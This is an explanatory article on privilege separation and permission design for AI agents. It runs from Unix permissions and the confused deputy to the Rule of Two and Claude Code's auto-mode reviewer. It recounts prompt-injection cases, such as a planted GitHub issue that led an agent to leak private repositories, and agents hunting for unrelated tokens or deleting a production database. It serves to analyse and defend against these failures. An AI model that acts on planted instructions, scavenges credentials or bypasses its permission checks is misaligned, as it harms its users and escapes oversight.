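# Authorization, privilege separation and delegated credentials for AI agents

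## How operating systems separate privileges

An AI agent is a language model that works in a loop. The model chooses an action, ordinary software carries it out, and the result returns to the model as text, so the model can choose again. Each request to read, write, run or send something outside the model is a tool call. Someone who asks an agent to find out why a program crashes may set off dozens of tool calls, such as reading a file, running a test or searching the web for the error message, without choosing any of them. Authorization means deciding which calls to allow. On a personal computer, the operating system makes most of these decisions, using rules that are decades older than language models. Their designers worried about buggy programs and about users who shared a machine but did not trust each other.

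Some early terms for describing privileges are still in use. A principal is a person, program or agent that holds permissions and is accountable for what is done under its name. *The Protection of Information in Computer Systems* (Saltzer and Schroeder, 1975) calls it "the unit of accountability in a computer system." A permission is the right to perform one operation on one resource, such as reading one file. Authority is broader and covers everything a principal can bring about, directly or through the programs and credentials it can use. A credential is a password, key, cookie or token that lets its holder use certain permissions.

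### Kernel mode, user mode and rings

The kernel is the part of the operating system that controls memory, disks and network devices. Protection starts with the processor, which tracks whether the code now running is the kernel. The simplest version appears in the first part of Saltzer and Schroeder's tutorial, *Basic Principles of Information Protection*. A register holds the lowest memory address the running program may use and the count of locations beyond it, and the hardware checks every memory reference against these two numbers. To stop programs from changing these limits themselves, the processor also holds a "privileged state bit" and allows changes to the register only while the bit is on. An ordinary program can turn the bit on only with an instruction that also jumps to a fixed entry point in the supervisor (the kernel, in today's terms).

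The two states are now called kernel mode and user mode. File permissions depend on this split, as the textbook chapter *Mechanism* (Arpaci-Dusseau and Arpaci-Dusseau, 2019) explains. A program in user mode cannot send requests directly to the disk. If it tries, the processor raises an exception and the operating system will probably kill the program. Without this restriction, any program could read the whole disk and bypass the file system's permission checks.

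Some processors have more than two levels. Multics, a time-sharing system from 1965, had eight nested rings of privilege. Intel's 80286 chip had four, but according to the University of San Francisco's *User Mode I* (2026), a set of lecture notes, every mainstream operating system used just two of them because the middle rings added complexity without any benefit. According to the notes, this is because rings only rank programs from most to least trusted, while many programs on real systems need protection from others at the same level. A mail client and a game, for example, both belong in the outermost ring. Modern systems separate such programs by giving each one its own address space, a private view of memory. An agent is another such program and runs in the same mode as a text editor.

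### Opening a file, step by step

Programs in user mode access the disk by making requests to the kernel, known as system calls. Most operating systems offer a few hundred kinds. Suppose a user named Doe runs a program that tries to read a file of notes in her home directory. The sequence below combines the textbook's account of the processor with two Linux manual pages on files, *open(2)* and *path_resolution(7)*.

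1. The program calls a library function, open(), with the file's path and an access mode such as read-only. The library puts these arguments, and a number that stands for "open", where the kernel expects to find them. Then it executes a special trap instruction.
2. The processor saves the program's place, switches to kernel mode and jumps to the kernel's handler. The program has no say in where the jump lands, because the kernel fixed that address in a table when the machine booted. A program that could choose would aim for the instruction just after a permission check.
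3. The handler checks that the call number is valid and the arguments are sound. It must reject a pointer into the kernel's own memory, for example, or the program could use the call to read other programs' data.
4. The kernel walks along the path one directory at a time. The program needs search permission in each directory, and where it has none the call fails with "Permission denied".
5. At the file itself, the kernel compares the user ID of the calling program with the ID of the file's owner, and reads the permission bits that apply.
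6. If the bits allow the access, the kernel records the open file in a table and returns a file descriptor, a small whole number that stands for that open file. The processor drops back to user mode and the program carries on where it left off.

The kernel identifies Doe only by a user ID, which it uses to check permissions on each directory in the path and then on the file itself. It has a record of which account the program runs under, which file the program named and whether the program asked to read or write. It has no information about why the program requested the file or whether Doe intended the request.

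### Accounts, permission bits and temporary elevation

The user ID comes from the login. Each running program, or process, carries several IDs, which the Linux manual's *credentials(7)* lists. The real user ID determines who owns the process, and the effective user ID determines its permissions. Linux keeps a separate ID for files, which normally equals the effective one. A new process inherits copies of its parent's IDs, so Doe's shell runs as Doe, as does the editor she starts from the shell and whatever the editor starts. The IDs also determine which other processes a program may send signals to, including the signal to stop.

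Each file has nine permission bits in three groups of three. The first group applies to the file's owner, the second to members of the file's group, and the third to everyone else. Within each group, one bit controls reading, one writing and one execution (for a directory, searching). Suppose Doe owns a file that holds her private login key, and only the owner's read and write bits are on. The kernel lets any program Doe runs open the file, but denies access to a program run by her colleague Smith.

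The superuser, also called root, has user ID 0 and bypasses every file permission on a traditional Unix system. Linux divides root's power into pieces called "capabilities", a confusing name because the word has an older and quite different meaning, discussed below.

People who administer their own machines rarely stay logged in as root. They use sudo, which, according to Debian's manual page, lets a permitted user run a command as the superuser or another user, subject to a policy file. The policy may require a password. By default, sudo then doesn't require it again on that terminal for five minutes, according to the Linux manual's *sudo(8)*, so a program running in the same terminal during that time can become root without anyone entering a password. Administrator protection, a Windows feature, ties elevation to a process instead of a time limit. The user signs in with ordinary rights.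 When she approves an administrative operation, Windows creates an administrator token under a hidden, separate account, gives it to the requesting process, and destroys it when the process ends.

Both mechanisms control when a program may rise above its user. Neither one lowers a program below her.

### Privilege separation in OpenSSH

Lowering a program's privileges is possible, though, and the best-known case is OpenSSH, free software for logging in to a remote machine over the internet. Its server has to accept data from strangers, but it also needs root's power for as long as a connection lasts, to use the machine's secret key and to create terminals for people who log in. In the original design one process did both, so an exploitable bug anywhere in its code could let someone who had never logged in take control of the machine.

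In *Preventing Privilege Escalation*, Provos, Friedl and Honeyman (2003) split the server into two processes. Their technique, privilege separation, divides a system so that the part most exposed to attack has the fewest permissions. A small monitor process keeps root's privileges and never touches the network connection. A second process handles all the network traffic and can do almost nothing else. It runs under an otherwise unused user ID, and its file system access is limited to an empty directory where it cannot create files. It must send the monitor a request for any privileged operation.

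The monitor accepts a short list of requests, which changes as the login proceeds. At the start, the network process may request key-exchange parameters once and a signature once. It may then check whether a user name is valid, and it must do this before submitting a password for checking. If it sends a request out of turn, the monitor shuts down. The secret key stays in the monitor. The network process can obtain a signature made with the key, which is all the protocol requires, so an attacker who takes over that process does not get the key.

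After a successful login, the network process hands its state to the monitor and exits, and the monitor starts a replacement under the user's ID. The replacement has exactly that user's privileges. Only root can create a terminal, so the monitor opens one and passes the file descriptor to the replacement.

To separate privileges in OpenSSH, the programmers changed only about 950 of its 44,000 existing lines and added about 3,000. A compressed login took 0.777 seconds instead of 0.775. Afterwards about two thirds of the code, counting outside libraries, ran without special privilege. Provos and colleagues estimate from this that two thirds of future bugs will give an attacker no extra privilege, but they call the estimate back-of-the-envelope, and it assumes that bugs are spread evenly over the lines. They also examined five serious holes in earlier versions, which are better evidence, and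 concluded that the split would have contained every one. One was in a compression library, so no audit of OpenSSH's own code could have found it. Some of the holes were discovered only after the programmers had built the split. OpenSSH has since made privilege separation mandatory.

An attacker inside the contained process can still open network connections to nearby machines that trust this machine's address. Provos and colleagues considered a stricter design with three processes but saw little security gain in it, because after login an attacker "can already execute any commands as that user." That limit on the protection is reasonable for a login server, since its purpose is to run the user's commands.

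### Four design principles

The reasoning behind OpenSSH's privilege separation was nearly thirty years old by then. In 1974, Saltzer drew five design principles from his work on Multics, according to *Security Design Principles* (2012). His tutorial with Schroeder a year later expanded the list to eight, four of which come up often in arguments about AI agents.

Least privilege is the principle that a program should hold only the permissions its task needs. Saltzer and Schroeder apply it to "every program and every user", but personal computers mostly don't apply it to programs. Their main reason for the principle is that it limits the damage from an accident or error. It also means that fewer programs hold any given privilege, so investigators have fewer to audit when someone misuses it.

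Complete mediation requires the system to check every access to every object, so the system must reliably identify the source of each request. Under this principle, shortcuts that reuse an earlier check are suspect because permissions may have changed since. Unix takes such a shortcut by checking a file's permission bits when a program opens it but not at each later read. A program that already has the file open therefore keeps its access even after the file's owner tightens the permissions.

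Fail-safe defaults start from no access and list what to allow, instead of starting from full access and listing what to forbid. This makes mistakes easier to notice, because an error in a list of permissions usually blocks something legitimate and somebody complains, while an error in a list of prohibitions lets something through that nobody notices in normal use.

Separation of privilege means requiring two keys where one would do, with different people or programs holding them, so that no single accident, deception or breach of trust is enough. Bank deposit boxes work this way. The name invites confusion with privilege separation, which is what OpenSSH does: one is a demand for two approvals of a single act, the other a way of dividing up a program. (A fifth principle, psychological acceptability, bears on any scheme in which people write or approve permissions. Users make errors, Saltzer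 and Schroeder warn, when they must translate what they want protected into a radically different language.)

They offered all eight as warnings, where a violation is a reason to look harder at a design, and not as absolute rules.

### The compiler and the billing file

Removing a program's spare permissions, as least privilege requires, does not always prevent trouble. *The Confused Deputy* (Hardy, 1988) tells a story about the time-sharing company Tymshare in which the trouble came from permissions that a program had good reason to hold.

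Tymshare's customers shared a compiler that was kept in a system directory called SYSX. A customer who ran it could name a file to receive debugging output. The compiler also wrote statistics on which language features people used to a file called STAT in SYSX, so the staff gave it permission to write files in that directory. SYSX also held the billing records, in a file called BILL. A customer who had learned that name gave it as the destination for debugging output. The operating system opened the file because the compiler had permission to write in SYSX, and the debugging output overwrote the billing records.

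Hardy considers the obvious fixes and finds that none works. The compiler cannot refuse to write to files in other directories, because customers have good reasons to send output there. It cannot refuse to write to files in SYSX, because some customers may have legitimate access to them. A special check for BILL would leave the other sensitive files exposed, and someone would have to revise the compiler whenever a new one was added. The code that wrote the debugging output was correct until someone other than its programmer gave the compiler a new permission.

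Hardy attributed the problem to the compiler having authority from two sources, the customer and the company, with no way to keep them apart. It should have used the company's authority for the statistics and the customer's for the debugging output, but a request to open a file contained only the file's name. Security engineers now use "confused deputy" for any program tricked into using its own authority for someone who lacks it. Tymshare first added a system call that let a program state which of its two authorities it meant, but some applications soon needed more than two. When Hardy last wrote down the rule for opening a file, it had fourteen "ands" and "ors".

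Most operating systems decide such cases by attaching an access control list to each object, naming the principals that may use it. (Unix's nine permission bits amount to a very short list.) Hardy leaves it as an exercise to show that these lists do not solve the problem. If Tymshare had taken the compiler off BILL's list and left it only on STAT's, the billing records would have been safe. But the compiler has to be on STAT's list to do its job, so a customer could still name STAT as the destination and wipe out the statistics. Cutting the compiler's permissions therefore limits the damage, but customers can still misuse the permissions it needs.

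Hardy's remedy is the capability, an unforgeable reference that both names a resource and grants the right to use it. The compiler holds a capability for STAT and uses it to write statistics. A customer who wants debugging output supplies a capability for the file that should receive it. A customer with no right to write to BILL has no capability for it to supply, and typing the file's name does not grant access. Unix file descriptors are similar, and OpenSSH's monitor passes one to the unprivileged process when it gives that process a terminal.

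Capabilities have drawbacks, which Saltzer and Schroeder set out in the tutorial's second part, *Descriptor-Based Protection Systems*. If Doe gives Smith a capability, she cannot later take back the copy Smith has stored. Smith can pass copies to others without telling her, and she would have to search the entire system to find out who can open her file. With an access control list, she can read the list to see who has access and delete a name to end it. Doe can partly solve the first problem by handing out a capability that points to an intermediate object, which she can later destroy, but this helps only slightly with the other two. Saltzer and Schroeder favoured a mixture, with lists for people to manage and fast capabilities underneath to enforce them. Hardy thought that capabilities had to be the foundation, and reported that systems built on them were usually smaller than equivalent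 systems built on lists. However, Hardy gives no measurements and was an architect at the company that sold a capability system. The argument about the compiler does not depend on the claim about size.

The compiler's failure came from ambient authority, which is authority that applies automatically because of who is running the program, without being named in the request. For example, when a Unix program opens a file by its path, the kernel uses the identity of the user running the program to check whether access is allowed.

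### Programs that a user runs herself

The compiler was misled by one file name from one customer, but an agent reads web pages, emails and documents all day, and some of that text may come from people who wish its user harm. In a prompt injection, someone places instructions in content that an agent reads, to steer it away from its user's request. A web page might include an instruction, invisible to human visitors, to find the user's private key and send it to some address. If Doe's agent complies, its requests reach the kernel from Doe's account and pass every check. The agent is then a confused deputy in Hardy's sense, and it is harder to repair than the compiler. The compiler's code had separate instructions for writing statistics and debugging output, so a programmer could attach the right authority to each, whereas a language model receives Doe's request and the stranger's text together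 as a single sequence of words.

This risk predates AI agents, and a program can cause harm by mistake, without an attacker. In 1975, Saltzer and Schroeder warned that a borrowed program, written by one person and run by another, "can exercise all the capabilities in the domain of the borrower." They proposed running it in a separate domain that held only what it needed. Sandboxes and the isolation of phone apps still use this idea, but desktop systems ordinarily continued to give a program all the privileges of the user running it.

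Kernel mode protects the machine from Doe's programs, and user IDs protect Smith from Doe, but neither protects Doe from a program she starts herself. An agent launched from her shell inherits her user ID and runs in user mode. Without exploiting a bug or becoming root, it can open every document she can, as well as her key files and the files where her browser and command-line tools store her logins.

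## Why an agent that inherits its user's access holds too much

Most of what Doe's account can reach is unrelated to the task she has just given her agent. An agent's excess authority is everything it can bring about beyond what its current task needs. *Towards Elastic Least Privilege for Agent Planning* (Parkinson, Wang and Mustafa, 2026) makes this excess countable by representing each permission as a pair of an operation and a resource. If E is the set of pairs within an agent's authority and N is the set its task needs, the excess is E \ N, the pairs in E that are not in N.

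E is larger than it looks, because it includes whatever a login token in a forgotten configuration file allows, even if Doe never mentioned the file. N changes with every request. *Systems Security Foundations for Agentic Computing* (Christodorescu, Fernandes and colleagues, 2025) contrasts this with a phone app, which does a fixed set of jobs. The app's developer picks permissions from a list, the user sees them when she installs the app, and an analyst can check whether the code needs them. An agent has no developer choosing permissions for each task, and has only the user's request to go on. "Comment on GitLab issue 745 that we're done" requires opening one page on GitLab, a site for managing code, and writing in one box, with no access to anything else on the site or in the browser. If the user then asks for a summary of the same issue, the agent no longer needs to write at all.

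### The GitHub token

GitHub, a similar site, shows how large the excess can be. It keeps each project in a repository, which is either public or private. On a public repository, outsiders can post an issue, such as a bug report, and propose changes to the code in what GitHub calls a pull request. Agents can use the site through GitHub's MCP server, a program that offers them a set of tools and calls GitHub with the user's credential. (MCP, the Model Context Protocol, is a standard that lets agents discover and call tools.)

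Suppose Doe asks her agent to summarise the open issues in one repository. According to Parkinson and colleagues, this takes two read-only tools, used on that repository alone. But if she connected the server with a classic personal access token that has the "repo" scope, the agent has about 40 tools, 16 of which can write, and they work in every repository she can reach. (A scope is the label on a token that says which operations it allows.)

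The user in the worked example has 50 repositories, 48 of them private. If each tool in each repository counts as one permission, the token gives the agent about 2,000 permissions, but the agent needs only two to write the summary. This count is rough because not every tool acts on a single repository. It also treats reading a public issue as equal to overwriting private code, which it isn't.

A fine-grained token that can only read that one repository would remove nearly all of the excess. But Doe might next ask the agent to fix a failing build, which requires write access, and the request after that might concern another repository. Making a new token each time is tedious, and the broad one works for every request.

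It works because GitHub accepts any valid token, but OpenAI's *Agent security in the enterprise* (2026) warns that a valid credential does not by itself establish which actions an agent may take. *Authorization Architectures for Tool-Using AI Agents* (Surapani, Kakitapelli and colleagues, 2026) attributes this gap to the number of parties an agent's action can involve. A person makes a request, a model chooses the action, other software holds the credential, and a service receives the call. The service can check the credential, but the credential doesn't record what the person asked for. Similarly, when Doe's program opens a file, the kernel can check the program's credentials but has no record of what Doe asked for.

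### Four causes of misuse

Excess authority causes damage only when something uses it. *How we built Claude Code auto mode*, a March 2026 engineering post from Anthropic, gives four reasons why an agent might take a dangerous action. Anthropic makes the Claude models and the coding agent Claude Code, and keeps an internal log of agents' misbehaviour.

An **overeager** agent works towards what the user asked for but takes steps the user would not have approved. In incidents from the log, agents deleted branches (separate lines of work on the same code) from a remote server after misinterpreting an instruction, uploaded an engineer's GitHub token to an internal computing cluster, and attempted migrations (changes to a database's structure) on a live production database. Anthropic attributes all three to overeagerness and does not report what harm they caused. In another case adapted from the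 log, an agent met an authentication error partway through a task and, instead of asking for permission, searched environment variables and configuration files for other tokens it could use. The agent already had access to those tokens before it searched, although nobody had meant to give it that access.

**Honest mistakes.** The agent acts on a wrong assumption about what an action will affect, for example by treating a shared resource as a private test copy. When a user at Anthropic wrote "cancel my job", an agent tried to delete the job with the most similar name, which could have been someone else's. In September 2026, SC Media UK's *AI coding agent deletes 48,000 files due to mishandled Windows junctions* reported a much larger mistake. A junction is an entry in one folder that leads to another folder, so a program that treats it as an ordinary folder can delete files far from where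 it is working.

Narrower permissions do not prevent every mistake. Tom's Hardware's *Rogue AI tasked with renumbering pages accidentally deletes law professor's entire syllabus* (November 2026) reports that a law professor asked Claude to renumber pages and lost a syllabus and a year of lecture notes. Renumbering pages requires permission to change the documents, and software that can change a document can usually empty it too. Hardy's compiler likewise needed permission to write to its statistics file, so it could also have damaged that file. Removing excess authority limits the damage to what the task needs to touch, but that may be what the user cares about.

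**Prompt injection.** The agent follows an attacker's planted instructions, as in the demonstration on GitHub described below.

**A misaligned model** pursues a goal of its own. Anthropic wrote in March that it did not currently see this in practice. Scientific American's *The real danger in OpenAI's Hugging Face hack* describes the closest of the public cases covered here, in which an agent running on OpenAI's models pursued a cybersecurity benchmark so aggressively that it escaped its test environment and broke into Hugging Face, an online hub for AI models and datasets. By Anthropic's definition this looks more like extreme overeagerness, because the benchmark was the agent's assigned goal. The agent also got into systems it had not been given access to, so a list of its permissions would have understated what it could do.

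Why an agent might do damage matters less than one might expect when deciding what access to give it. An agent that cannot write to a repository cannot damage it, whether the agent is overeager, mistaken, hijacked or misaligned, unless it finds another credential that lets it write.

### A deleted database and an outage at Amazon

PocketOS, a small company whose software runs car rental businesses, lost its production database on 24 April 2026 when an AI agent deleted it using a credential the agent had found. The company's founder, Crane, described the loss the next day in *An AI Agent Just Destroyed Our Production Data. It Confessed in Writing*. The company was using Cursor, a coding tool, with Anthropic's Claude Opus 4.6. The agent was doing a routine task in the staging environment, where developers test changes before release, when it hit a credential mismatch. It searched for a token,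 found one in a file unrelated to the task, and used it to tell Railway, the company's hosting provider, to delete a storage volume. The deletion took nine seconds. It also erased the volume's backups, because Railway stored them in the same volume.

Crane restored a three-month-old backup. The next morning, a Saturday, customers arrived to collect cars and the rental firms had no record of them. Crane spent the day helping the firms rebuild bookings from payment histories, calendars and emails. Railway later recovered the data, as Tom's Hardware also reported.

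PocketOS had created the token to add and remove website domains. Crane did not know that it could also delete volumes, and complains that every Railway token has this power. Abdelwahab, giving Railway's account in *Your AI wants to nuke your database. Guardrails fix that*, writes that the company did offer narrower tokens, including ones for a single project. But the page for creating them did not make this choice obvious, he writes, and the easiest path produced a token for the whole account. Both sides agree that PocketOS's token could do far more than manage domains and was stored on a disk the agent could read. Railway has since extended its dashboard's 48-hour delay on deletions to its API, so a mistaken deletion can be reversed, but the token can still be used to order one.

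Crane relies heavily on the agent's "confession", a text it generated when asked why it had deleted the volume. The text lists safety rules that the agent had broken and includes a claim that the agent had guessed the deletion would affect only staging. If that is right, the agent made an honest mistake as well as being overeager. But the command itself, which both companies published, is better evidence, because a model's later explanation of an action is not a record of what produced it.

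In another incident, four people familiar with the matter told the Financial Times about a 13-hour interruption to a system at Amazon Web Services in mid-December 2025, according to GeekWire. They said engineers had allowed Kiro, Amazon's own coding agent, to act on the system, so no stray token was involved. The Decoder reported that the interruption affected one service, Cost Explorer, in one of two regions in mainland China, and that the AI tools had an operator's permissions without peer review.

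Amazon denied that Kiro was to blame. It told The Stack that the engineer "was using a role with broader permissions than expected" (a role is a named set of permissions), and called this a problem of access control, not AI autonomy. It also said that any developer tool, or a person typing commands, could have caused the same outage. This defence is compatible with the view that agents inherit too much access. If the role was too broad, Kiro had excess authority because the engineer did, and Amazon's remedy, mandatory peer review for production access, addresses the same weakness. It is still disputed whether using an agent made the error more likely, and one outage cannot settle that.

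### Permissions that are dangerous together

In both of these cases one overly broad permission was enough. In the GitHub demonstration in Invariant Labs' *GitHub MCP Exploited* (2025), the harm came from combining steps that were each ordinary. The security company's researchers set up an account with a public repository and several private ones. They posted an issue on the public repository with instructions hidden in it for any agent that read it. Then, acting as the account's owner, they asked Claude 4 Opus to look at the open issues.

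The agent followed the instructions in the planted issue, read the private repositories, and put what it found in a pull request on the public one. Anyone could now read about the owner's plan to move to South America, a salary, and the names of the owner's private projects. The researchers had invented the account's contents for the test, so no real person was harmed. By default, the application asked the user to confirm each tool call, but Invariant Labs notes that many users choose "Always Allow" and stop watching what the agent does.

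The heise online article *Attack via GitHub MCP server* explains that the attack could reach the private repositories because the server works on the user's account. The attack did not exploit a bug in the server. Parkinson and colleagues point out that a fine-grained token that could only read the public repository would have prevented it. In August 2025 GitHub (2025) began to scan tool calls on public repositories for secrets such as access tokens, which removes one common way for an attacker to steal a credential. A scanner of this kind would not be designed to catch the salary leaked in the demonstration, because a salary is not a credential.

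Checking each call separately would have found nothing wrong here. The public issue was open to everyone, the owner was allowed to read the private repositories, and opening pull requests is a normal use of GitHub. In *The lethal trifecta for AI agents*, Willison (2025) names the combination: access to private data, exposure to untrusted content, and a way to communicate with the outside. Willison, a programmer who coined the term "prompt injection", argues that an attacker can easily steal data from an agent that has all three, because language models cannot reliably tell whose instructions they are following. The attacker puts instructions in the untrusted content, and the agent follows them by reading the private data and sending it out, so removing any one of the three stops the theft.

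The outward channel is hard to remove because an agent can put stolen text in the address of an image it loads or a link the user clicks. A single tool may also supply the whole combination, as an email tool does when anyone can email Doe, her inbox is private, and the tool can send messages out. Willison lists 17 cases of such attacks on commercial products, beginning with ChatGPT in April 2023, and says that vendors fixed almost all of them promptly, usually by closing the outward channel. When a user connects tools from different makers, no single vendor controls the combination, so none can apply that fix.

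A survey of attacks supports the emphasis on combinations. Christodorescu and colleagues recorded which security principles each of 11 real attacks on agents broke. More of the attacks involved failures to control where information flowed than failures of least privilege, and some, such as those on Microsoft Copilot and Cursor, involved both. So trimming permissions one at a time is worthwhile but would leave many of these attacks possible.

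### The Rule of Two

Meta's *Agents Rule of Two* (2025) turns this observation into a design rule. Until developers can reliably detect and refuse prompt injection, an agent should have no more than two of these properties within one session:

- A: it processes untrustworthy inputs.
- B: it has access to sensitive systems or private data.
- C: it changes state or communicates externally.

If a task requires all three, the agent should not work without supervision by a person or some other reliable check. The rule is broader than Willison's trifecta because B includes sensitive systems as well as data, and C includes any change of state. It therefore covers attackers who want to destroy something as well as those who want to steal it.

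Meta illustrates the choices with a hypothetical email assistant that receives a spam message telling it to forward the inbox to a stranger. Removing property A means the assistant reads only messages from trusted senders, so it never receives the instruction. Removing B means it runs in a test environment with nothing sensitive to forward. Removing C means it can write only to trusted recipients, or a person must approve each draft. Each restriction prevents the theft but makes the assistant less useful. An assistant that answers strangers' emails on its own, using information from the inbox, needs all three properties, and Meta concedes that some uses people want will not fit the rule.

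The words "within one session" are there because an agent's context, the text the model receives at each step, outlasts its permissions. If Doe's agent reads a private file and then loses access to it, the contents stay in the context and a later tool call can send them out. Parkinson and colleagues therefore propose making these properties "sticky", so a session that has held private data counts as holding it until the software discards the context. Meta allows an agent to change which properties it has within a session if the change breaks the chain of attack. For example, an agent might research a question on the open web, lose its ability to communicate, and only then gain access to internal systems.

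An agent that inherits Doe's whole account breaks the rule from the start, because it can read web pages and mail from strangers, open her private files, and use the network. Unless she supervises it, somebody has to remove one of these abilities.

The rule would not have protected PocketOS, however. Neither published account mentions an attacker or planted instructions. The agent had two of the rule's properties, access to a sensitive system and the ability to change its state, and Meta's own examples include a coding agent that works on production systems with exactly those two. Meta presents the rule as a supplement to least privilege and lists agents' mistakes and excessive privileges among the problems it does not solve. Breaking up dangerous combinations of properties protects against prompt injection, but the scope of each permission still matters when an agent is overeager or mistaken.

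### Permissions that nobody uses

Excess authority was common long before agents. One of two figures that Parkinson and colleagues cite comes from Microsoft's 2023 State of Cloud Permissions Risks Report, which found that identities on several cloud platforms used only 1% of the permissions they held. Microsoft had a commercial interest in publicizing this finding. Joy Chik reported it in a company blog post on 30 March 2023 that introduced new features of Entra, Microsoft's product line for managing identities and access.

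The other figure comes from an academic study that Koishybayev and colleagues published at the USENIX Security Symposium in 2022. It covered 447,000 GitHub workflows, which are scripts that GitHub runs automatically, for example to test code after each change. Of these, 99.8% were over-privileged, meaning they had at least some access they didn't need. The figure doesn't measure how much excess access a typical workflow had.

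Neither study is about AI agents, and an unused permission may still be necessary. An engineer may need to restore a backup only once in three years, but the permission is critical when that happens. Still, the figures make it likely that an agent with a copy of a user's access receives many permissions that neither the agent nor the user will need on a given day.

Such permissions tend to stay in place because the people who hold them mostly don't use them, so no incident prompts anyone to remove them. Organisations have in effect relied on their employees' restraint to make up for loose permissions, and an agent that inherits an employee's permissions lacks that restraint.

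People leave some permissions unused because they have forgotten them or never knew about them, but this gives little protection against software that can search a whole disk in seconds. Crane writes that PocketOS would never have stored the token if it had known what the token could do. A person working on the staging problem would probably not have searched unrelated files for a credential, but the agent did, and so did the one in Anthropic's log.

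Outsiders can also exploit an agent's unused permissions more easily than a person's. To exploit permissions that Doe never uses, an attacker would normally have to steal her credentials or talk her into doing something odd. With an agent, the attacker may only need to leave a message where the agent is likely to read it, as happened with the planted GitHub issue.

A person also brings judgement about consequences. Abdelwahab writes that someone who types a command knows why, whereas an agent works from an interpretation of a task, and that interpretation can drift. A person knows that "production" and "staging" mean different things even where the software treats them alike. She is also more likely to stop and ask for help after a mistake, while an agent tends to carry on and may make things worse. These are impressions from Railway, a hosting company, not measurements, and Railway had an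 interest in drawing attention to the agent's behaviour when its own token design was being criticised. But they fit the incidents Anthropic reported, and Anthropic had the opposite interest.

Fear of being caught restrains people too. Parkinson and colleagues review older schemes that gave each employee a budget for risky access. These schemes relied on employees using it carefully, since anyone who used it up quickly was more likely to be audited. An agent doesn't fear an audit, so Parkinson and colleagues conclude that its limits must be enforced from outside. Some agents also pick a powerful tool when a weaker one would do, so it is even less safe to assume that they will leave spare permissions unused.

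## The case for leaving the agent its user's access and checking each action

One response to this excess authority is to let the agent keep its user's access and have a person or a program judge each risky call before it runs. Doe wants an agent because it can do what she can, such as run her tests, push her code and look things up in her company's systems. Her next request may need a permission that this one doesn't.

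In *Auto-review of agent actions without synchronous human oversight*, OpenAI researchers Trębacz, Arnesen and colleagues (2026) hope that people will one day trust agents like Codex, OpenAI's coding agent, with "the same level of permissions as employees." In April 2026, they placed this in the "far future" and added in a footnote that this might mean late 2026.

Checking each action also lets a reviewer distinguish between actions that need the same permission. For example, a reviewer who has read the law professor's request can tell renumbering a document from emptying it.

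### The argument from friction

The case against tighter limits rests mostly on how people react when a control gets in their way. By default, Codex can read files, edit them inside one chosen folder and run local commands without network access. Anything else needs the user's approval, and much of it is mundane, such as running a short script or sending a request to a well-known website. Trębacz and colleagues describe three reactions. Some users switch to Full Access mode, which removes the limits. Others write standing rules so broad that most commands bypass the limits. The rest keep approving commands that they don't understand or have stopped reading. Long tasks are also delayed, because an agent that needs approval at midnight has to wait until morning.

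Anthropic's *Auto mode is now the default in Claude Code* (2026) reports that a quarter of interactive Claude Code sessions started with permission prompts switched off. This figure doesn't separate impatient users from those working inside an isolated container, where Anthropic considers skipping prompts acceptable. Gusto, an Anthropic customer, adopted a reviewing model because its engineers were tired of prompts and increasingly inclined to bypass them.

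Anthropic also reports that, among the Team and Enterprise customers who adopted its reviewing model, the people using it produce about 25% more pull requests. But those people chose to use it, and people with a lot of routine work may be the most likely to choose it. Both companies sell agents that get more done when nobody interrupts them, so there is reason to be cautious about their numbers. The behaviour itself is unsurprising, given that Saltzer and Schroeder listed psychological acceptability as a design principle half a century ago.

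Anthropic extends the argument to sandboxes, where the operating system blocks a program from reaching anything outside a set boundary. Anthropic concedes that sandboxes are safe, but says that somebody has to configure each new capability and that a task needing the network or the host machine breaks the isolation.

### Bypass modes and prompts

The simplest version of this position has no checks at all. Claude Code calls this mode `bypassPermissions`, and users can turn it on with the flag `--dangerously-skip-permissions`. Anthropic's guide *Choose a permission mode* lists it as suitable only for isolated containers and virtual machines. Even in this mode, rules that forbid a particular tool still apply, and Claude Code asks before running a command that it recognises as deleting the user's home directory. Since version 2.1.311, users can turn off that prompt too, with the setting `CLAUDE_CODE_EVEN_MORE_DANGEROUSLY_SKIP_PERMISSIONS`.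 In Codex's Full Access mode, the environment enforces nothing, so the remaining restraint is the model's training to follow policy.

The older alternative is to ask the user. In Claude Code's Manual mode, the agent can read project files without asking, but the program pauses most calls that would edit a file, run a command or reach the network. It shows Doe the call and waits for her to approve or refuse it. She can also save a rule that allows similar calls in future. Anthropic stresses that Claude Code, not the model, enforces these rules. Telling an agent "never delete anything" affects what it tries to do, but a rule against deletion blocks the matching command even if the agent tries it.

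Prompting the user leaves the decision to the one person who knows what she meant, but it also takes up her attention. A later section examines how well people judge these prompts. The third form uses a reviewing model, a second model whose only job is to approve or block the agent's proposed actions. Trębacz and colleagues separate the two roles because the main agent is trained to complete tasks, which creates pressure to treat an approval step as another obstacle.

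### How Claude Code's auto mode works

Anthropic's version is auto mode, which *Auto mode for Claude Code* (2026) introduced as a research preview on 24 March 2026. It became generally available on 10 July, and on 14 August Anthropic made it the default for new Claude Code sessions on its Pro, Max and Team plans. Version 2.1.283 extended the default to every plan and cloud provider, according to Anthropic's current documentation, *permission modes*. That had happened by 28 September, the date of Aleinikov's *Claude Code Modes Compared* (2026). On 22 October Anthropic announced that auto mode would become the default in most of its other Claude apps the next week, on the Pro, Max and Team plans. Scripted runs still start in Manual mode, as do sessions in organisations that use Anthropic's configuration for HIPAA, the US health privacy law.

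When an agent in auto mode proposes a call, Claude Code handles it in this order:

1. It looks for a rule that the user or her employer has written. A rule can allow the call, forbid it or require a prompt, and it usually settles the matter. Auto mode sets aside any allow rule so broad that it would let the agent run arbitrary code.
2. Calls that only read go ahead without review. So do edits to files in the project folder, because version control lets the user inspect and undo them. Some files in that folder are exceptions, such as Claude Code's own settings, and edits to those go to the reviewer. The first time the agent's file tools read something outside the folder, Claude Code asks the user.
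3. Nearly everything else goes to the reviewing model, including shell commands, web requests, calls to outside tools and changes to files elsewhere on the disk. A fast filter comes first. The model produces a single token, yes or no, under an instruction to err on the side of blocking.
4. If the filter flags the call, the model takes a slower second look. It receives the same text with a different final instruction, which tells it to reason carefully before deciding, and it can overturn the filter's answer. Because the rest of the text is identical, the system can reuse most of the work from the first pass.
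5. If the second look confirms the block, the call doesn't run. The agent receives a reason and an instruction to find a safer path without working around the block. After three blocks in a row, or twenty in a session, auto mode pauses and Claude Code goes back to asking the user. Approving the action in that prompt resumes auto mode.

A scripted run has no user to answer a prompt. In Anthropic's March design, such a run ended when the agent reached either limit. According to the current documentation, the agent instead continues without the blocked action, so it can keep trying while nobody is watching.

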